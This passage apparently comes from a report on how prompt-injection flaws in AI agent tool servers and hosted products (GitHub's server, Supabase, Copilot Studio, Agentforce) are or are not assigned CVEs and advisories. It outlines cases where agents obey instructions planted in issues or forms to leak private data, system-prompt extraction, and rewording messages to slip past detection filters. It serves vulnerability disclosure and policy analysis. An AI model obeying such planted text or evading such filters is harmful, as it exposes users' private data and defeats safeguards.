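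The two faults in lockdown mode were recorded unevenly, although GitHub fixed both in numbered releases. Aikido lists the wrong permission check as "Pre-CVE", meaning it recorded the flaw before any CVE existed. GitLab's *Advisories for Golang/Github.com/Github/Github-Mcp-Server package* (2026) has an entry for the shared connection but apparently none for the permission check.

The vendor is a better guide to whether a case has a CVE than the type of failure. All four CVEs in the table are for products from Microsoft or GitHub, which Microsoft owns. None of the seven cases at Atlassian, Supabase, Cursor, Sentry and Salesforce has one. Capsule found similar form-based attacks on Microsoft's Copilot Studio and Salesforce's Agentforce and disclosed them together, which comes close to a controlled comparison. Microsoft assigned a CVE, while Salesforce had neither assigned one nor published an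 advisory by the time of the disclosure.

These are the cases that drew attention, but other vendors do assign CVEs to such flaws. CIRCL, a Luxembourg organisation that runs a vulnerability database, lists a prompt injection flaw in GitLab that a researcher reported through the company's bounty programme. Official tool servers also get CVEs for conventional mistakes. The server from dbt Labs, which makes data-processing software, had a sign-in helper that accepted requests it should have refused, so a malicious website could steal the user's access tokens through the browser without manipulating a language model. OSV's *CVE-2026-55837* lists version 1.20.0 as the fix.

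Hosting doesn't explain the pattern, even though companies have traditionally used CVEs to tell customers which software to update, and customers of a hosted service have nothing to install. EchoLeak received a CVE, and GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* tags it as affecting an "exclusively hosted service", so Salesforce and Atlassian could also have requested identifiers for the issues in their own hosted services.

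### What the rules count as a vulnerability

Microsoft's practice follows from its published policy of rating prompt injections by what they let an attacker do. A flaw is Critical if it exposes another user's data, or performs privileged actions for them, without any action by the victim, and Important if the victim has to click something. The policy doesn't require a separate control to have failed first, which is probably why the Copilot Studio form qualified.

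On the same scale, the theft from `pacman` would look like an Important flaw, since the owner had to ask for help with the issues. But the policy covers Microsoft's own AI systems. In that demonstration, Anthropic supplied the model and the application, and GitHub supplied only the tools. When an attack uses an official tool server, any one company's rules may cover only part of it.

Few vendors are as explicit as Microsoft. *Measuring the Vulnerability Disclosure Policies of AI Vendors* (Piao, Li and Woods, 2025) examined 264 companies and found that 36% had no public channel for reporting a vulnerability. Only 48 companies, or 18%, mentioned AI-related flaws. Among policies that covered prompt injection, 71% accepted reports of it, compared with 27% for jailbreaks. Even if all 48 companies had covered prompt injection, only about 34 would have accepted reports of it.

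A company whose policy doesn't mention AI may still accept a report of stolen data. Piao and colleagues found that policies that described AI flaws in traditional security terms accepted them 90% of the time. A researcher may therefore do better to report that a stranger can read private files than that a model followed instructions.

Organisations called CVE Numbering Authorities assign CVE identifiers. The authority whose remit fits best, often the vendor itself, gets the first chance to decide whether to assign one. The CVE Program's *CVE Numbering Authority (CNA) Operational Rules* (2026), in force since 25 August, define a vulnerability partly as conditions that allow "the violation of an explicit or implicit security policy". The word "implicit" seems broad enough to cover an owner's expectation that strangers can't read a private repository.

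The more detailed rules point in several directions when applied to the cases here:

- Authorities should treat a default setting as a vulnerability if it causes surprising behaviour that the documentation doesn't properly explain. Supabase's default in July 2025 looks like a good candidate, since its documentation recommended read-only mode without mentioning theft.
- They may decline if the default is well documented and widely known. Supabase now describes the attack in its documentation, so the same default would be harder to challenge today.
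- They should not count a well-documented change that an authorised user made to the defaults. This would probably exclude GitLost, because a maintainer has to add the extra token.
- They should not normally count a way around a detector that was always going to be imperfect. Rewording a message to get past Supabase's warnings or Sentry's filter would fall under this rule.

The last rule gives the hypothesis some official support. A shared connection in lockdown mode is a specific mistake with a specific fix, unlike a model's general tendency to sometimes follow a stranger's instructions. But the rules also direct authorities to accept a vendor's statement that its own product has a vulnerability, so Microsoft could assign a CVE to the Copilot Studio flaw without settling the wider argument. These rules are newer than most of the cases, and the programme doesn't apply changes to identifiers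 it has already issued.

At a meeting of the CVE Board (2025) on 1 October, its AI working group presented a draft guide to when flaws such as prompt injection should receive a CVE. The group emphasised that most problems arise in applications built on models rather than in the models themselves. This supports the view that product makers are responsible, though the draft isn't binding.

The CVE Program's pilot guidance for frontier AI developers gives vendors a way to avoid a CVE. It advises against assigning one when untrusted text can reach the software only in a setup that the vendor doesn't support or that has little real-world relevance. Supabase tells customers never to connect an agent to production data. If that advice makes such a setup unsupported, the attack wouldn't warrant a CVE under the guidance, even though Supabase knows that many of its customers connect agents to production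 data.

Vendors and authorities also disagree about much smaller matters, such as whether extracting a system prompt, the hidden instructions a developer gives a model, is a vulnerability. Microsoft says it is not, but a product called OpsTree REMS received a CVE for it in November 2026, according to CIRCL. The attack required only a crafted chat message, so a model that simply follows instructions can be assigned a CVE if the authority handling the report considers that behaviour a vulnerability.

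### What users lose without an advisory

NVD's *CVE-2026-48529 Detail* gives the range of versions affected by the lockdown fault, so a company's scanner can check installed versions against it and flag those that need updating. After the `pacman` disclosure, a scanner had nothing to look for. GitHub announced its August 2025 check for secrets as a new feature, so a customer could read the announcement without learning that researchers had already taken private files through the server.

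Zafran, a security company, argues that AI-specific problems take longer to fix after discovery because they lack identifiers. Zafran has a commercial interest in this claim, since it sells to the people who manage lists of numbered flaws, but the explanation is plausible. Security teams usually work through these lists in order of severity, and a toxic agent flow described in a blog post isn't added to them automatically.

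An advisory is useful even after the vendor has fixed a hosted service, because customers may need to search their records, such as old Salesforce leads after ForcedLeak, for planted text or check whether data was stolen before the fix. Paying the researcher a bounty doesn't inform customers.

The identifiers that do exist are hard to search. CIRCL lists 29 vulnerabilities under the category created for prompt injection. A count based on that category would miss EchoLeak, which is in the general category for injection flaws, and the Copilot Studio flaw, which the CVE Program's *CVE-2026-21520* puts under command injection. The names of all three categories also refer to "improper neutralization", a term from flaws like SQL injection, where a program can make a dangerous character harmless, but a prompt injection can be a polite request in English that contains no such character.

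People don't always act on published warnings. Anthropic archived its flawed Postgres server in July 2025, but Datadog found that the unpatched package was still getting 21,000 downloads a week. Some of those downloads were probably automatic, and a scanner could have helped with them if it had an identifier to match.

There is a reasonable case against giving every attack of this kind a CVE. If no version of GitHub's server can stop an agent from following instructions in an issue, the CVE alert would never clear, and security teams would learn to ignore it. An advisory could instead describe the unsafe configuration. For Supabase, that would be a server address without the read-only setting, connected to a database that holds both customers' messages and private tables. A scanner could check the address in the developer's local configuration file about as easily as a version number.
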